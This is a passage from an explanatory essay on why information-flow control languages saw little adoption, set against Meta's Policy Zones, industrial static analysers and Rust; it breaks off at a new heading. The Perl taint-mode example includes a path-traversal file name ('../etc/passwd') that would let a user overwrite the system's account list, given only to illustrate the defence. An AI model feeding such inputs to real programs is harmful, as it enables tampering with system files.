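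A mistake in one of these files can undo the whole guarantee. Askarov and Sabelfeld found one in Jif's signature for "arraycopy", a standard Java method that copies items from one list to another. The signature didn't record that the method changes the destination list. They showed that the Jif compiler would therefore accept a short program that copied a secret list into a public one. Like the compiler, the signature was part of the trusted computing base, but it had probably received much less attention.

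### A new language, and policies nobody had written

To use Jif, a team had to leave ordinary Java. The poker program could not use Java's standard way of converting objects to text to send over a network, because Jif did not support it for classes with adjustable labels, so Askarov and Sabelfeld wrote the conversion code by hand for every class. They also complained that Jif lacked debugging tools and thorough documentation, and said that programmers had to debug a separate version written in an ordinary language. A company that chose Jif would have faced the same problems, and would also have had to train its programmers and hope that a university kept maintaining the compiler.

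The compiler also needs rules for who may see what, and in most organizations nobody had written them down in a form it could use. A company might promise in its privacy policy to protect customer data. But a Jif programmer needs to know whether a support agent may see a customer's address and whether the answer changes when the customer closes the account, and somebody in the legal department may have to decide.

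JPmail's builders ran into this problem. Their client sent a message only if it had encrypted the text with a method the recipient trusted. Jif's labels could express the basic restriction but not each person's own list of preferences, so the builders wrote a separate policy file and generated part of the program from it. Whenever the file changed, someone had to recompile the client. Jif 3.0, which Chong and colleagues developed for SIF, partly solved this by letting users set policies while a program was running. A calendar user could show some people the details of an event and others only its time.

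Every programmer wants a program to stay within its own memory, so the designers of a memory-safe language such as Rust can build one rule into the compiler for everyone. But confidentiality rules depend on the application, and two companies with nearly identical software may want different ones. Better compilers would have reduced the false alarms in information-flow languages, but someone would still have had to write each application's policy.

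### Later languages and libraries

Researchers have responded to most of these problems. Paragon, another extension of Java, replaced Jif's single declassify command with "locks" that a program opens and closes. A programmer can write a policy that a player's key becomes public once the "end of game" lock is open, and the compiler checks the program against it. The poker program no longer needed the seal when it was rebuilt in Paragon. But Paragon is also a new language, so a company adopting it would still have to retrain its programmers and convert its code.

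Other researchers tried to avoid a new language by checking flows while a program runs, which is hard to do correctly. Suppose h is secret, l is public and holds 0, and the program runs "if (h) l := 1". A simple monitor could mark l as secret when the assignment happens. But when h is false, the assignment never happens and l stays public, so an observer who can read l learns that h was false. The usual solution is to stop the program before it changes a public variable inside a branch on a secret. This prevents the leak, but it can also stop a program that a user relies on.

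Chudnov and Naumann used this technique, known as "no sensitive upgrade", for JavaScript. A web page often combines code from several companies, and the browser's usual protections do little to stop one company's code from misusing data that another company's code handles. Chudnov and Naumann inserted the monitor into the page's code because changing the browser was impractical. They also named excessive runtime overhead as a difficulty for the field, and a monitor that checks each operation as it happens always adds some overhead.

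Libraries fit existing languages more closely because they need no change to the compiler. Haskell, a language popular with researchers, already separates calculations from actions that affect the outside world, so a library can wrap a secret in a special type and control which functions may unwrap it. Several groups built such libraries from the mid-2000s on. One of them, LIO (2011), keeps a current label that rises as the program reads secrets, and blocks writes to anything less secret than that label. The label works much like Jif's program-counter label, except that LIO checks it while the program runs. But Haskell has far fewer commercial users than Java, so these libraries had a small audience from the start.

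Rust may be a better candidate, because companies already use it. Cocoon, a Rust library that Ada Lamba and colleagues published in 2024, works with the ordinary Rust compiler. Programmers put code that handles secrets inside marked blocks. The result of a block is secret, and the code inside cannot affect public data outside it, so its branches can't leak secrets through ordinary variables. The researchers added Cocoon to parts of two existing programs, a Spotify client and the Servo browser engine, without the complete rewrite that Jif required. A 2025 successor, Carapace, added labels that can change while a program runs and labels for trustworthiness.

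Rust also removes a large source of false alarms. Null pointer errors caused 455 of the 725 false alarms in King and colleagues' study, and they mostly do not arise in Rust because its ordinary references always point to something. Errors from reading past the end of a list remain, and programmers still have to decide what to label and what to release. If they mark only part of a program, only that part is protected.

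None of these designs clearly passes the adoption test. Jif came closest to meeting the condition about outside users, since the people who built JPmail and the poker program had not created the language. But they were information-flow researchers willing to spend months on problems that would have made a commercial team give up. The published case studies for Cocoon and Carapace are by the libraries' own developers, and neither library is known to be used in a commercial product. Both are recent, so their record is weaker evidence of their prospects than Jif's is after more than 25 years.

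SPARK, a subset of the Ada language for high-integrity software, is a partial exception. A commercial firm, Praxis, developed it with a built-in check on which outputs of a procedure depend on which inputs. But as Chong and colleagues note, SPARK checked only simple dependencies and did not support declassification or labels that change as a program runs. Companies that wanted to track sensitive data through large systems have generally built their own tools, as Meta did with Policy Zones, instead of adopting a language from a university.

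## Where has information-flow tracking worked in production?

Information-flow tracking has reached production mostly in forms that require much less work from programmers than Jif did. Perl's taint mode needs no labels in the source code, and SPARK's flow contracts need only a few lines per procedure. Meta's more ambitious Policy Zones tracks personal data across the software behind products such as Facebook and Messenger, and it took years to make practical.

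### Perl and SPARK

Perl, a scripting language behind many early websites, has a taint mode that a programmer turns on with a single switch. Perl then marks data from outside the program as tainted, including typed input and the contents of files, and the mark spreads to anything computed from that data. If the program tries to use tainted data to run a command or change a file, Perl stops it:

```
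$name = <STDIN>;                  # typed by the user, so tainted
open(F, ">", "/reports/$name");   # Perl stops the program here
```

Without the check, a user could type "../etc/passwd" and make the program overwrite the computer's list of accounts, if the program had permission to write there. To use the name safely, the programmer extracts the part that matches a pattern, such as letters and digits only, and Perl treats the result as trusted. This is a form of endorsement, but Perl doesn't check whether the pattern is sensible, so a pattern that matches everything removes the taint from any input.

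Perl's taint tracking, like most, ignores implicit flows, which is reasonable when the attacker supplies the input but not the code. The bug tracker Bugzilla and the spam filter SpamAssassin run in taint mode. Ruby offered a similar feature but dropped it in 2022.

SPARK checks flows before the program runs, and it does catch implicit ones. The programmer can attach a contract that lists, for each output of a procedure, the inputs it depends on. For a password check, it might look like this:

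```
procedure Check (Guess, Stored : in String;
                 Match    : out Boolean;
                 Attempts : in out Natural)
  with Depends => (Match    => (Guess, Stored),
                   Attempts => Attempts);
```

Here Match depends on the guess and the stored password, but the count of attempts may depend only on its own previous value. If a programmer increases the count only after a wrong guess, the count depends on the stored password through a branch, and SPARK's analyzer reports the mismatch. SPARK also avoids most of the exception alarms that troubled Jif's users, because its programmers separately prove that errors such as reading past the end of a list can't happen.

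NATS, which runs British air traffic control, and the chipmaker Nvidia both use SPARK. But SPARK's information-flow contracts are optional, and its analyzer can work out the dependencies itself, so not all SPARK users write contracts. The contracts also can't label data as secret, so a reviewer has to know that a stored password, for example, is secret and notice if a contract lets it reach the wrong output.

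### How Policy Zones applies a new rule

Meta built Policy Zones to enforce purpose limitation, the principle that a company should use personal data only for the purposes it stated when collecting it. Meta had relied on "if" statements in its code and on lists of who could open each dataset. The access lists forced engineers to store data for different purposes separately, and the "if" statements needed repeated audits as the code changed. Neither method tracked the data after a permitted program copied it elsewhere.

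The company explains the replacement with a made-up example rule that lets its products use banana data for smoothies and fruit baskets but not for banana bread. Engineers apply the rule in five steps.

1. They attach the label BANANA_DATA to the database that holds the data. A set of rules tells Policy Zones which purposes the label permits.
2. A web request called BananaRequest reads the database. Nobody has labeled the request, so Policy Zones can't tell what it will do with the data and flags a violation.
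3. An engineer labels the request, which creates a "Banana Zone" around it. Policy Zones now checks where the request sends data, and flags writes to two logs, logB and logC.
4. The engineer labels logB as banana data too, and removes the banana data from what the request writes to logC.
5. With no violations left, the engineer switches the zone from logging mode to enforcement. If a programmer later adds a write to a destination outside the zone, Policy Zones blocks it.

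A zone can also start partway through a request. If BreakfastRequest calls a function that makes a banana smoothie, the engineer can put the zone around only that function and everything it calls.

Each violation has one of three remedies:

| Flow | What the engineer finds | Remedy |
|---|---|---|
| Safe | The data is going somewhere for an allowed purpose | Label the destination |
| Unsafe | The purpose is not allowed | Block the access |
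| Reclassified | The program reads the data, but none of it reaches the destination | Mark the flow as permitted |

A reclassified flow might be a request that reads a banana record to test the database, then writes only the time of day to a log.

Logging mode probably made adoption possible. Jif's compiler rejected a program until the programmer had dealt with every alarm, whereas Meta's products could keep running while engineers resolved the violations. During that time, however, Policy Zones does not protect the data. Logging also finds only the flows that occur while it is on, so a violation in code that runs once a year may not appear until enforcement blocks it.

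To check a write, Policy Zones has to identify which zone the current function belongs to, even after a long chain of calls. Hack, Meta's main web programming language, has an experimental feature that probably does this job. HHVM's *Memoization Options*, a page of Hack's public documentation, calls it an "implicit context", a value that passes automatically from each function to the ones it calls. Many functions save their results to avoid repeating work, so a function could compute something inside the Banana Zone and later return the saved result to a request outside it. To prevent this, Hack requires such functions either to keep separate results for each context or not to use the context at all, and it stops any that break the rule. HHVM's *Available Contexts and Capabilities* lists related "zoned" features as reserved for Meta's internal use. Neither page names Policy Zones, but the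 features they describe closely match it.

### Queries in the data warehouse

Much of Meta's data ends up in a warehouse that its analysts and AI teams query, mostly in SQL, the standard database language. An SQL query names the tables it reads and writes, so Policy Zones can check it before it touches any data. Meta gives the example of a daily job that counts how many messages each user sent. A simplified version is:

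```
INSERT INTO messages_sent
SELECT user_id, COUNT(*)
FROM message_metadata
GROUP BY user_id
```

The input table carries the label MESSAGING_DATA. A parser works out the query's inputs and outputs, and a policy service then checks them. Write labels(t) for the labels on a table t, allowed(g) for the purposes that a label g permits, and p for the purpose of the job. In simplified form, the service requires, for every input table t:

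```
labels(t) ⊆ labels(output)
p ∈ allowed(g)   for every label g in labels(t)
```

The first condition is Denning's rule with sets of labels as the security classes, so the output must be at least as restricted as everything that went into it. The second condition restricts the purposes the data can be used for. In the example, the first condition requires the messages_sent table to carry MESSAGING_DATA too, and the second requires the label to permit the purpose of the count.

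If the query passes, the policy service issues a cryptographically signed token, which the job presents when it opens the tables. Meta needed the token because its older permission service checked each request separately. It could check a request to read table A and a request to write table B, but it could not detect that data from A was going into B.

If the output table lacks the label, the system sometimes adds it automatically. Otherwise it shows the engineer an error and suggests fixes. Labeling a table that jobs already use is riskier, since enforcement could break those jobs. Meta's tools first simulate the effect, then set aside the flows that would fail and track them until an engineer has resolved each one.

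Labels spread in the warehouse much as they did in Jif. Any table computed from message data inherits that data's label by default, even if the job used the data only incidentally. Engineers can stop the spread by reclassifying the output, but each label has its own rules for doing so. Meta may accept expert review for some labels, or a technique such as differential privacy, which adds random noise so that a result reveals little about any one person.

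Meta applies the same approach to training AI models. A job that trains a spam filter on message data must carry the MESSAGING_DATA label, and so must the finished model. Meta's *Scaling Privacy Infrastructure for GenAI Product Innovation* (2025) describes a similar rule for data from its AI glasses, under which a training job on protected data starts only if every dataset it uses permits that purpose.

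### What went wrong first

Meta began with basic uses in its data warehouse. It described its designs for web and backend code as "quite abstract", and the first large project to use them ran into serious trouble. Engineers had to work out how the designs applied to real code and build missing operational support. Meta now advises finishing one complete use case before building anything general.

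In Meta's first annotation system, each annotation described both the data and all the rules that applied to it. When a program combined data subject to several requirements, the annotations conflicted in ways that engineers struggled to resolve. Meta's labels now record only the kind of data, and each requirement has its own rules for those labels, which a team can change without affecting anyone else's.

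Meta says the warehouse's original policy language could describe nearly every exception, so engineers did not need reclassification, but they found it very hard to understand why the system had blocked something. Meta replaced the language with flat, readable labels and moved the exceptions into reclassification. This made most cases easier to understand but left more decisions to case-by-case review.

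Marsala (2025), in *Purpose Limitation with Policy Zones*, lists three early designs that Meta had to replace:

- passing policies automatically from service to service
- using a single policy for every privacy requirement
- checking every access to a data store at one central point

The single policy probably failed for much the same reason as the combined annotations. A central check at the data store is close to the reference monitor Anderson's panel wanted, and it may have shared the weakness of Meta's old permission service, which could check a request for data but could not determine where the data would go next.

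Another obstacle was the computing overhead of checking flows, which was at first "prohibitively high" on Meta's busiest systems. The company simplified how it stored and compared policies, added support for zones to its programming languages, and standardized the annotations. These changes made the checks ten times more efficient. But Meta doesn't report the original overhead, so it could have fallen from 50 percent to 5 percent or from 5 percent to 0.5 percent.

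Meta also built tools for its engineers too late. It concentrated on making the technology correct, and engineers who did not understand how to label their data made mistakes that had to be fixed later. The company then developed Policy Zone Manager, a set of tools that finds flows, proposes labels and guides engineers through the remedies. Meta credits these tools with cutting the work "by orders of magnitude", again without giving hours. Kirti (2025), in the talk *Using GenAI to Accelerate Privacy Implementations*, still called adoption challenging because of Meta's size and the expertise required, and described using generative AI to help.

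### Finding the data to label

Before its engineers could label data, Meta had to inventory its millions of datasets and other assets and record what each contained, which took several years. It then mapped where data goes by analyzing code and by comparing the data that enters and leaves a sample of running requests.

Meta illustrates the comparison with the religious views entered in Facebook Dating. If a user enters "Buddhist" and the same word appears in a log, the tool can report with high confidence that the data flowed there. But if a user enters two religions and the program logs only the count, 2, the values don't match. The tool sends such cases to human reviewers as low-confidence candidates, along with many unrelated pairs.

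Labels also have to match the meaning of the data. Meta's *Privacy-Aware Infrastructure in the AI-Native Era* (2026) describes a field named "age" that could hold a person's age or the time before a temporary file expires. Labeling the file's expiry time as personal data would restrict a whole system unnecessarily, and failing to label a person's age would leave it unprotected.

Fixed rules determine about 85 percent of these classifications, and a language model handles the rest, using roughly 400 times as much computing for each one. At those rates, the model would account for almost 99 percent of the computing, which helps explain why Meta turns the model's stable answers into fixed rules. People must approve any new rule that could weaken protection.

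Meta also warns against judging the classifier by accuracy alone. If one field in a hundred is sensitive, a classifier that labels every field harmless is 99 percent accurate but misses every sensitive field. Meta does not report how many sensitive fields its own classifier misses.

### What Meta gave up

Policy Zones has direct links to university research. Lucas Waye, who presented it at a Swedish university in 2025, wrote a doctorate under Stephen Chong, one of the builders of SIF. In *Policy Zones*, Waye (2025) called it an information-flow control system and listed familiar problems, including labels that spread too far and the need to manage reclassification. The system enforces a weaker property than noninterference. Meta calls its guarantees strong, but in its posts it neither states a property covering everything an observer could learn nor offers a proof.

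Policy Zones can block implicit flows as well as direct copying. Once a request is in the Banana Zone, the system blocks any write to an unlabeled log, whether the program copied banana data into it or only used the data to decide what to write. Fixing the zone in advance should also largely avoid the leaks through untaken branches that Austin and Flanagan describe in finer-grained systems in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*. The drawback is that more data is labeled unnecessarily and then has to be reclassified. A mistaken reclassification leaks data, just as a careless declassification would in Jif.

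The larger weakness is coverage, since some of Meta's systems do not use Policy Zones and still depend on the older checks. In the warehouse, Meta keeps some processing in separate silos because it can't yet trace what code outside SQL does with the data. The warehouse and the web code also run different versions of Policy Zones, and a separate process has to carry requirements from one to the other. AI agents may open further gaps. Mangtani (2026) warns in *Data Governance in the World of Agents* that agents leave sensitive data in new places, such as records of their actions and the output of their tools.

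These limits matter less for Meta than they would for a military system, because Policy Zones mainly has to stop well-meaning programmers from using data in the wrong place. Those programmers are unlikely to deliberately leak it through a program's timing.

Almost everything known about how well the system works comes from Meta. The company reports that the warehouse version checks tens of millions of data flows a day across hundreds of thousands of different queries. This shows heavy use, but Meta does not publish how many of those flows the system blocks, how many alarms are false, how often engineers reclassify data, or how much the checks slow things down. Without those figures, outsiders cannot tell how often the system prevents misuse or compare its false alarms with Jif's.

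### What the Federal Trade Commission contributed

Meta funded Policy Zones itself, under heavy pressure from the Federal Trade Commission (FTC), which enforces US consumer protection law. The FTC's *Stipulated Order for Civil Penalty, Monetary Judgment, and Injunctive Relief* (2019) settled claims that Facebook, as Meta was then called, had violated a 2012 privacy order. Facebook agreed to pay $5 billion, which the FTC described as the largest penalty ever imposed on a company for violating consumers' privacy. The new order runs for 20 years and requires regular outside assessments.

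One part of the order is a purpose limit. The FTC had accused Facebook of misrepresenting how it would use phone numbers that people provided for a security feature. The order, as quoted in World Privacy Forum's *Highlights of the FTC and DOJ Facebook complaint and order*, bars the company from using such numbers for advertising if it has "identified through its source tagging system" that people gave them for security. In Policy Zones terms, the phone number carries a label that rules out advertising.

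Protti (2025) wrote in *Reflecting on Meta's $8 Billion Investment in Privacy* that Meta's privacy infrastructure is "due, in large part" to the 2019 agreement. As Meta's chief privacy and compliance officer for products, Protti had every reason to present the program as a success, but crediting a regulator's penalty does not flatter the company, so the admission is fairly believable. The $8 billion covers the whole privacy program since 2019, including staff who review new products, and Meta has not said how much of it went to Policy Zones.

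Meta's *Upholding Our Commitment to Protecting Your Privacy* (2023), which the company published while fighting further restrictions from the FTC, gives some narrower figures. Meta had assigned more than 800 engineers to rebuild parts of its infrastructure for data protection, and a single two-year assessment had already taken more than 200,000 hours of auditing, or about 100 people working full time for a year. Meta wanted to show how much it was spending, but even much lower spending would give a company good reason to automate its checks.

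The FTC's pressure only partly explains why Meta chose information-flow control. The order made the obligation to limit how data is used hard to escape. Unlike the Orange Book's vendors, Meta will answer to assessors for two decades, whatever its customers prefer. But a company can also try to limit data use with access lists and audits, as Meta did at first, and a smaller company might find that cheaper. Meta's size made manual checks expensive.

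Policy Zones passes the three-part adoption test because it runs in Meta's products, engineers who did not build it use it, and it needs no research grant. But all the users Meta describes work for Meta. Other large companies have the same problem. IAPP's 2025 conference session *Automating Purpose Limitation with Meta, Microsoft, and LinkedIn* brought together three companies that use engineering to enforce limits on what data may be used for, though Microsoft and LinkedIn may not track flows as Meta does.

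## Why did static analysers and memory-safe languages spread?

Static analysers and memory-safe languages mostly enforce rules that almost every program should obey, so their users don't have to write policies first. Meta needed years to inventory and label its data for Policy Zones, but a company could try a static analyser and see real faults the same day. Most of the analysers that spread were also deliberately unsound, meaning that their makers let them miss some faults in order to raise fewer false alarms. Programmers stopped reading a tool's reports when too many of them were false.

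### How a bug-finder works

Suppose a payment program contains this code:

```
lock(account)
if amount > balance:
    return "refused"
balance = balance - amount
unlock(account)
return "paid"
```

The lock stops two payments from changing the same account at once. The programmer forgot to release it before returning "refused", so the next payment from that account will wait forever. A tester who tries one refused payment and stops there won't notice.

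An analyser follows each path through the code and keeps track of the lock:

```
enough money:      lock → pay → unlock → return    released
too little money:  lock → return                   still held: warning
```

It needs no specification of the payment system, only the general rule that a program must release every lock it takes.

False alarms arise when an analyser follows a path that the program can't take:

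```
if x > 0: lock(account)
write_log()
if x > 0: unlock(account)
```

An analyser that treats the two tests as unrelated will warn that the program might take the lock and never release it, which can't happen if x stays the same. To rule this out, the analyser would have to compare the two tests and work out whether write_log changes x, and write_log may call hundreds of other functions. When the analyser can't determine this, its maker has to decide whether it should warn.

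Coverity, a company that began selling a university bug-finder in 2002, usually accepted missing some bugs to avoid false alarms. *A Few Billion Lines of Code Later* (Bessey, Block and colleagues, 2010) explains that the tool ignored constructs that caused many false alarms and sometimes skipped whole files. These omissions also let it handle millions of lines of code with little setup. Most customers wanted it to finish overnight.

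### What customers did with the warnings

By the end of 2009 Coverity had about 700 customers. To win a customer, it usually sent a salesperson and an engineer, who ran its tool on the customer's code in the morning and presented the results that afternoon. They had no time to weed out bad warnings, and the engineer, who had written neither the tool nor the code, had to explain each fault on the spot.

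Programmers often called a warning false because they did not understand it. One wrongly insisted that the C standard lets a program write one position past the end of an array and, after a heated argument, proposed to "agree to disagree". Coverity dropped some checks because their warnings were too hard to explain. For years it didn't report errors caused by two parts of a program running at the same time, although it could find them without much difficulty.

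In Coverity's experience, users were liable to ignore a tool once more than 30 percent of its warnings were false. They then dismissed complicated but correct warnings as false, which made them trust the tool even less. The company aimed to keep false warnings below 20 percent in its established checks. By comparison, 82 percent of the warnings in King and colleagues' Jif study were false.

Some customers did not want a better tool. One company had fixed about 1,200 of the 2,400 faults that Coverity reported, then upgraded to a version that reported 3,600. The manager was furious because the new version seemed to have undone all the team's work. Managers earned bonuses when the number of faults fell, and some companies never upgraded. Coverity tried to keep each release from changing the results by more than 5 percent, which ruled out many improvements to the analysis.

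Missed faults hurt sales much less, because customers rarely learned of them. The main exceptions were faults a customer had planted as a test and known faults that disappeared from the results after an upgrade.

### Warnings during code review

Facebook learned how much the timing of a warning matters when it introduced Infer, an analyser based on academic research into program proofs. At first, Infer checked the whole Android app every night. *Scaling Static Analyses at Facebook* (Distefano, Fähndrich and colleagues, 2019) describes how the team picked 20 to 30 of the faults and assigned each to a suitable developer. The team thought fewer than 20 percent of the warnings were false, but developers fixed almost none of the faults.

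The team then had Infer comment on each code change when a developer submitted it for review. The fix rate rose to over 70 percent, with the same analysis and the same rate of false alarms. Developers explained that a warning about old code forced them to drop their current work and think about code they might never have worked on. During review they were already thinking about the code, and they had probably introduced the bug themselves.

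Timing may not explain the whole difference. Facebook's developers may have ignored the nightly list partly because fewer of its faults were worth fixing, since it included faults in code that people were already using without obvious trouble. In a later survey, Google's developers judged 74 percent of the problems flagged during compilation to be real, but only 21 percent of those found in code already in the company's repository. *Lessons from Building Static Analysis Tools at Google* (Sadowski, Aftandilian and colleagues, 2018) attributes the lower figure to testing and review having already caught the more important faults.

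Infer had to be fast to be used in code reviews. It computes a short summary of each function, such as "may return nothing", and uses the summary wherever other code calls that function. When a developer changes one function, Infer can reuse most of the other summaries, so it finishes in about 15 minutes on average. The summaries also let it find faults that span many functions, such as one in OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library, that took 61 steps to trace. By 2019 Facebook's developers had fixed more than 100,000 problems that Infer reported.

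Facebook also gave up a proof of safety to meet a deadline. Its researchers were building a tool to prove that a program has no data races, which occur when two parts of a program use the same memory at once and at least one changes it. The engineers behind the Android News Feed needed help sooner, so the researchers released a simpler race detector, RacerD. They instead proved that, under certain assumptions, an idealized version of RacerD reports only real races, though it may miss some. Developers fixed over 2,500 races in the year to March 2018.

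Facebook built a security analyser, Zoncolan, which uses taint tracking to find places where an attacker's data can reach a sensitive operation. It could check more than 100 million lines of code in under 30 minutes. Security engineers tolerated more false alarms than other developers, so they saw all of Zoncolan's results. Developers submitting code changes received comments directly only from its most reliable checks. Zoncolan found 43.3 percent of the severe security faults that Facebook detected, more than either manual reviews or outside researchers did.

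### Google's limits on false alarms

Google tried three times to get its engineers to use FindBugs, a Java analyser from university researchers. In 2006 it put the results on a dashboard, which few engineers visited. Staff then filed bug reports by hand, and during a week set aside for the task in 2009, engineers reviewed 3,954 warnings but fixed only 640 of the faults. Finally, Google posted the warnings as comments in code reviews, but too many were unhelpful, and engineers lost confidence in the tool.

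Google set stricter rules for its later tools. It counts a warning as an "effective false positive" if the developer takes no useful action, even when the warning is correct. Checks that stop a program from compiling must have no effective false positives, and the problems they report must be easy to understand and fix. Before turning on such a check, the team behind it fixes every existing case across Google's code so that developers don't face a backlog of old errors. Checks that comment during review may have up to 10 percent effective false positives.

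Tricorder, the platform that runs the review checks, has a "Not useful" button beside each warning. If complaints about an analyser pass the 10 percent limit, Google turns it off until its author improves it. In early 2018 Tricorder examined about 50,000 code changes a day. Each day, reviewers clicked "Please fix" more than 5,000 times and "Not useful" 250 times.

Programmers sometimes reported correct warnings as mistakes because the wording was unclear. One check covered a function that fills values into text but recognizes only the placeholder "%s", and it warned programmers who used any other. About once a week, someone reported that the check was wrong, though it never was. The complaints stopped after the team changed the message to say that only "%s" works.

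Google's management usually didn't require engineers to use static analysers, so the tools' makers had to keep engineers happy. That need also limited what the tools checked. As of 2018, Google used mostly simple analyses and considered more sophisticated ones too expensive to build for its two billion lines of code.

### Microsoft's driver verifier

Microsoft got closer to proof by concentrating on device drivers, the programs that let Windows control hardware such as printers and network cards. Faults in drivers caused 85 percent of Windows XP crashes, according to *Thorough Static Analysis of Device Drivers* (Ball, Bounimova and colleagues, 2006). Other companies wrote many of the drivers, but customers who saw a crash could easily blame Windows.

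Microsoft's Static Driver Verifier checks rules such as "take and release this lock in strict alternation". Its engine, SLAM, would deal with the false alarm in the x > 0 example as follows:

1. It builds a simplified program that has the same branches and function calls but records only whether the program holds the lock.
2. It searches the simplified program for a path that breaks the rule, and finds one that takes the lock and never releases it.
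3. It checks whether the real program could follow that path. The path requires x to be above zero at the first test but not at the second, which is impossible if x hasn't changed.
4. It adds "x > 0" to the facts that the simplified program records, and searches again. Both tests now give the same answer, so the false alarm disappears.

The simplified program can do everything the real one can, so if the search finds no violation, the driver obeys the rule. The proof still depends on a hand-written model of the rest of Windows.

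*A Decade of Software Model Checking with SLAM* (Ball, Levin and Rajamani, 2011) reports that the version of SLAM released with Windows 7 found 270 real faults in 140 drivers, even though Microsoft ran it after all its other tools. Its reports were correct 90 percent of the time for older kinds of driver and 98 percent of the time for a newer, simpler kind.

Writing specifications was practical because thousands of drivers could share the same rules. Formal verification experts wrote only 60 of the more than 210 rules in the Windows 7 version, and ordinary engineers and interns wrote or revised the rest, although a senior manager once complained that it took a PhD to write one. Designers of the newer driver interface changed the interface when a rule was hard to express. But SLAM could not handle programs of several hundred thousand lines or check how parts running at the same time interact.

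Microsoft dropped the verifier from its driver kit in 2024 in favour of CodeQL, which lets programmers search code for suspicious patterns as if it were a database. The *SDV Deprecation Announcement* says that CodeQL works on more kinds of driver project and has a dedicated team at GitHub. One developer replied that Microsoft had neglected its older tools until they were barely usable. The verifier had passed the adoption test for well over a decade, but it still depended on one company's willingness to maintain it.

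### Astrée and flight-control software

Airbus needed a sound analyser because its flight-control software already had very few faults. Mauborgne, one of the analyser's developers, notes in the slides *ASTRÉE* that bug-finders were expected to be useless to the company. A tool that finds most faults adds little when there are almost none, and finding no faults doesn't prove that none remain. Airbus wanted proof that its programs would never divide by zero, read outside an array or make similar errors while running.

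Astrée, which French researchers began building in 2001, proves this by calculating what values each variable could hold. Ranges alone are not always precise enough:

```
B = (X == 0)
if not B: Y = 1 / X
```

Astrée records that X lies between 0 and 100 and that B is true exactly when X is zero, so it can prove that the division by X is safe. If it recorded only the range, it would have to warn about a division by zero.

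In November 2003 Astrée proved that the main flight-control program of the Airbus A340, 132,000 lines of C, had no errors of this kind. The analysis took an hour and 20 minutes on an ordinary PC, according to École Normale Supérieure's *The Astrée Static Analyzer*.

Flight-control software suits this method unusually well. Engineers draw the controls as diagrams, and a program turns them into C code. The code runs as one endless loop that reads the sensors, calculates, sends commands and waits for the next clock tick. It doesn't request new memory while running, its functions never call themselves, and it uses pointers (variables that hold memory addresses) only in simple ways. Blanchet, Cousot and colleagues developed Astrée on a program that had run for ten years without such an error, so they could presume that every alarm was false (*A Static Analyzer for Large Safety-Critical Software*,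 2003). The same patterns recurred throughout the code, so one improvement could remove hundreds of alarms.

They needed that precision because someone has to investigate every remaining alarm before the proof is complete. They estimated that a 5 percent false-alarm rate on a program of a few hundred thousand lines would mean several person-years of work.

Two Airbus engineers later analyzed another control program, of about 200,000 lines. Delmas and Souyris, in *Astrée* (2007), report these results:

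| Stage | Alarms |
|---|---|
| First analysis | 467 |
| After Astrée's developers added a setting for more precise estimates in loops | 327 |
| After the engineers had Astrée consider certain table positions one at a time | 11 |
| At the end | 0 |

At least one of the last 11 alarms was real. The program checked that two hardware readings were large enough before it divided by their sum. But it read the hardware again for the division, and by then both values could have fallen to zero.

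The engineers were not experts in this kind of analysis, but they had close support from the people who built Astrée. Delmas and Souyris concluded that such a tool requires a "one-to-one customer-supplier relationship", because a change in the customer's program can bring back false alarms that only the toolmaker can remove. A company has sold Astrée since 2009, so it outlasted its research project. Larger software with many parts running at once was harder to analyse. After four years of work on a version for 1.6 million lines of such Airbus code, that version still produced many alarms, according to ANR, the French research agency that funded the work.

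### Why Rust spread

Rust gives ordinary programmers a sound check by having them write code that the compiler can analyze easily. Its central idea is ownership. Every piece of data has one owner, and Rust frees the memory when the owner goes out of use:

```
let a = vec![1, 2, 3];   // a owns the list
let b = a;               // ownership moves to b
println!("{:?}", a);     // error: a no longer owns the list
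```

Other code can borrow the data without owning it. At any moment, either several borrowers may read the data or one may change it, and no borrower may use it after its owner goes out of scope.

These rules prevent a program from using memory after freeing it, freeing it twice or creating a data race. C and C++ allow all of these errors, and attackers can often use them to take over a program. When the compiler can't tell whether an array position is valid, a Rust program checks it while running and stops if it isn't. None of this prevents mistakes in a program's logic, so a Rust login program can still accept the wrong password.

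Some necessary code, such as code that controls hardware directly, breaks the rules. Programmers put it in blocks marked "unsafe", where the compiler allows a few extra operations and the programmer is responsible for their safety. A mistake there can undermine the safe code around it. OffSeq's *Rust Adoption Drives Android Memory Safety Bugs Below 20% for First Time* describes a serious flaw in an unsafe block of CrabbyAVIF, a Rust library for reading images. Reviewers know where to look for this kind of flaw in Rust, whereas in C it could be almost anywhere.

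Rust code can also call C functions, and C code can call Rust, usually through a small amount of unsafe code. A company can therefore write one new component in Rust and leave the rest of its software unchanged. Chromium's developers, for example, rewrote in Rust the code that reads PNG images, web fonts and a common data format. The remaining C code can still corrupt memory that the Rust code uses, but each replacement removes some of the risk.

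Android shows what this can achieve over several years. Memory-safety flaws made up more than 70 percent of its vulnerabilities in 2019, and Vander Stoep (2025), who works on Android security at Google, reported that in 2025 they fell below 20 percent for the first time. The number of these flaws also fell, from 223 in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024 (The Hacker News, 2025), so the smaller share isn't just the result of an increase in other flaws. Rust is only part of the reason, because Android's developers also write new code in Java and Kotlin, which are memory-safe too.

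Google estimates that Android's Rust code has 1,000 times fewer memory-safety flaws per line than its C and C++ code. The true difference may be smaller, because researchers have had much longer to find flaws in the older code, but Rust code would still have far fewer flaws even if the estimate were several times too high.

Google's developers also had a more immediate reason to use Rust. They rolled back Rust changes only a quarter as often as C++ changes and spent 25 percent less time reviewing them. Teams chose where to use Rust, so easier projects or better programmers may have contributed to these differences. Still, a manager who cares only about delivery dates could reasonably choose Rust based on these figures. Jif's users, by contrast, spent extra months on labels and got no comparable saving.

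### Do unsound tools give false comfort?

A clean report from an unsound analyser can mean that the code is fine or that the tool didn't check it. A mistake made Coverity's early research tool ignore most uses of arrays for more than nine months without its builders noticing. Customers can be misled too. Bessey and colleagues say users knew in theory that the product did not prove anything, but reacted very differently when an upgraded version stopped reporting a few hundred known faults.

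The objection is not decisive, because for most software companies could not get a sound tool at a cost similar to that of an unsound one. Astrée needed years of specialist work for one family of programs. Programmers may also turn off a sound tool that raises thousands of false alarms, and then it protects nobody. Without an unsound tool, companies would often have relied on testing and review alone, which also miss faults.

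Companies can also measure some of what their tools miss. Facebook compared Zoncolan's results with faults that reviewers and outside researchers reported, and counted about 11 that the tool should have caught. That count is encouraging, but it excludes faults that nobody found. A company that cut back on reviews because its analyser reported few faults would lose even this evidence.

Sound tools can also create false confidence. Astrée relies on engineers to supply correct ranges for sensor readings, and Rust's guarantee depends on the code in unsafe blocks being correct. But these assumptions are written down, so a reviewer can check them, while an unsound tool's omissions may be scattered through its code.

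### What AI bug-finders change

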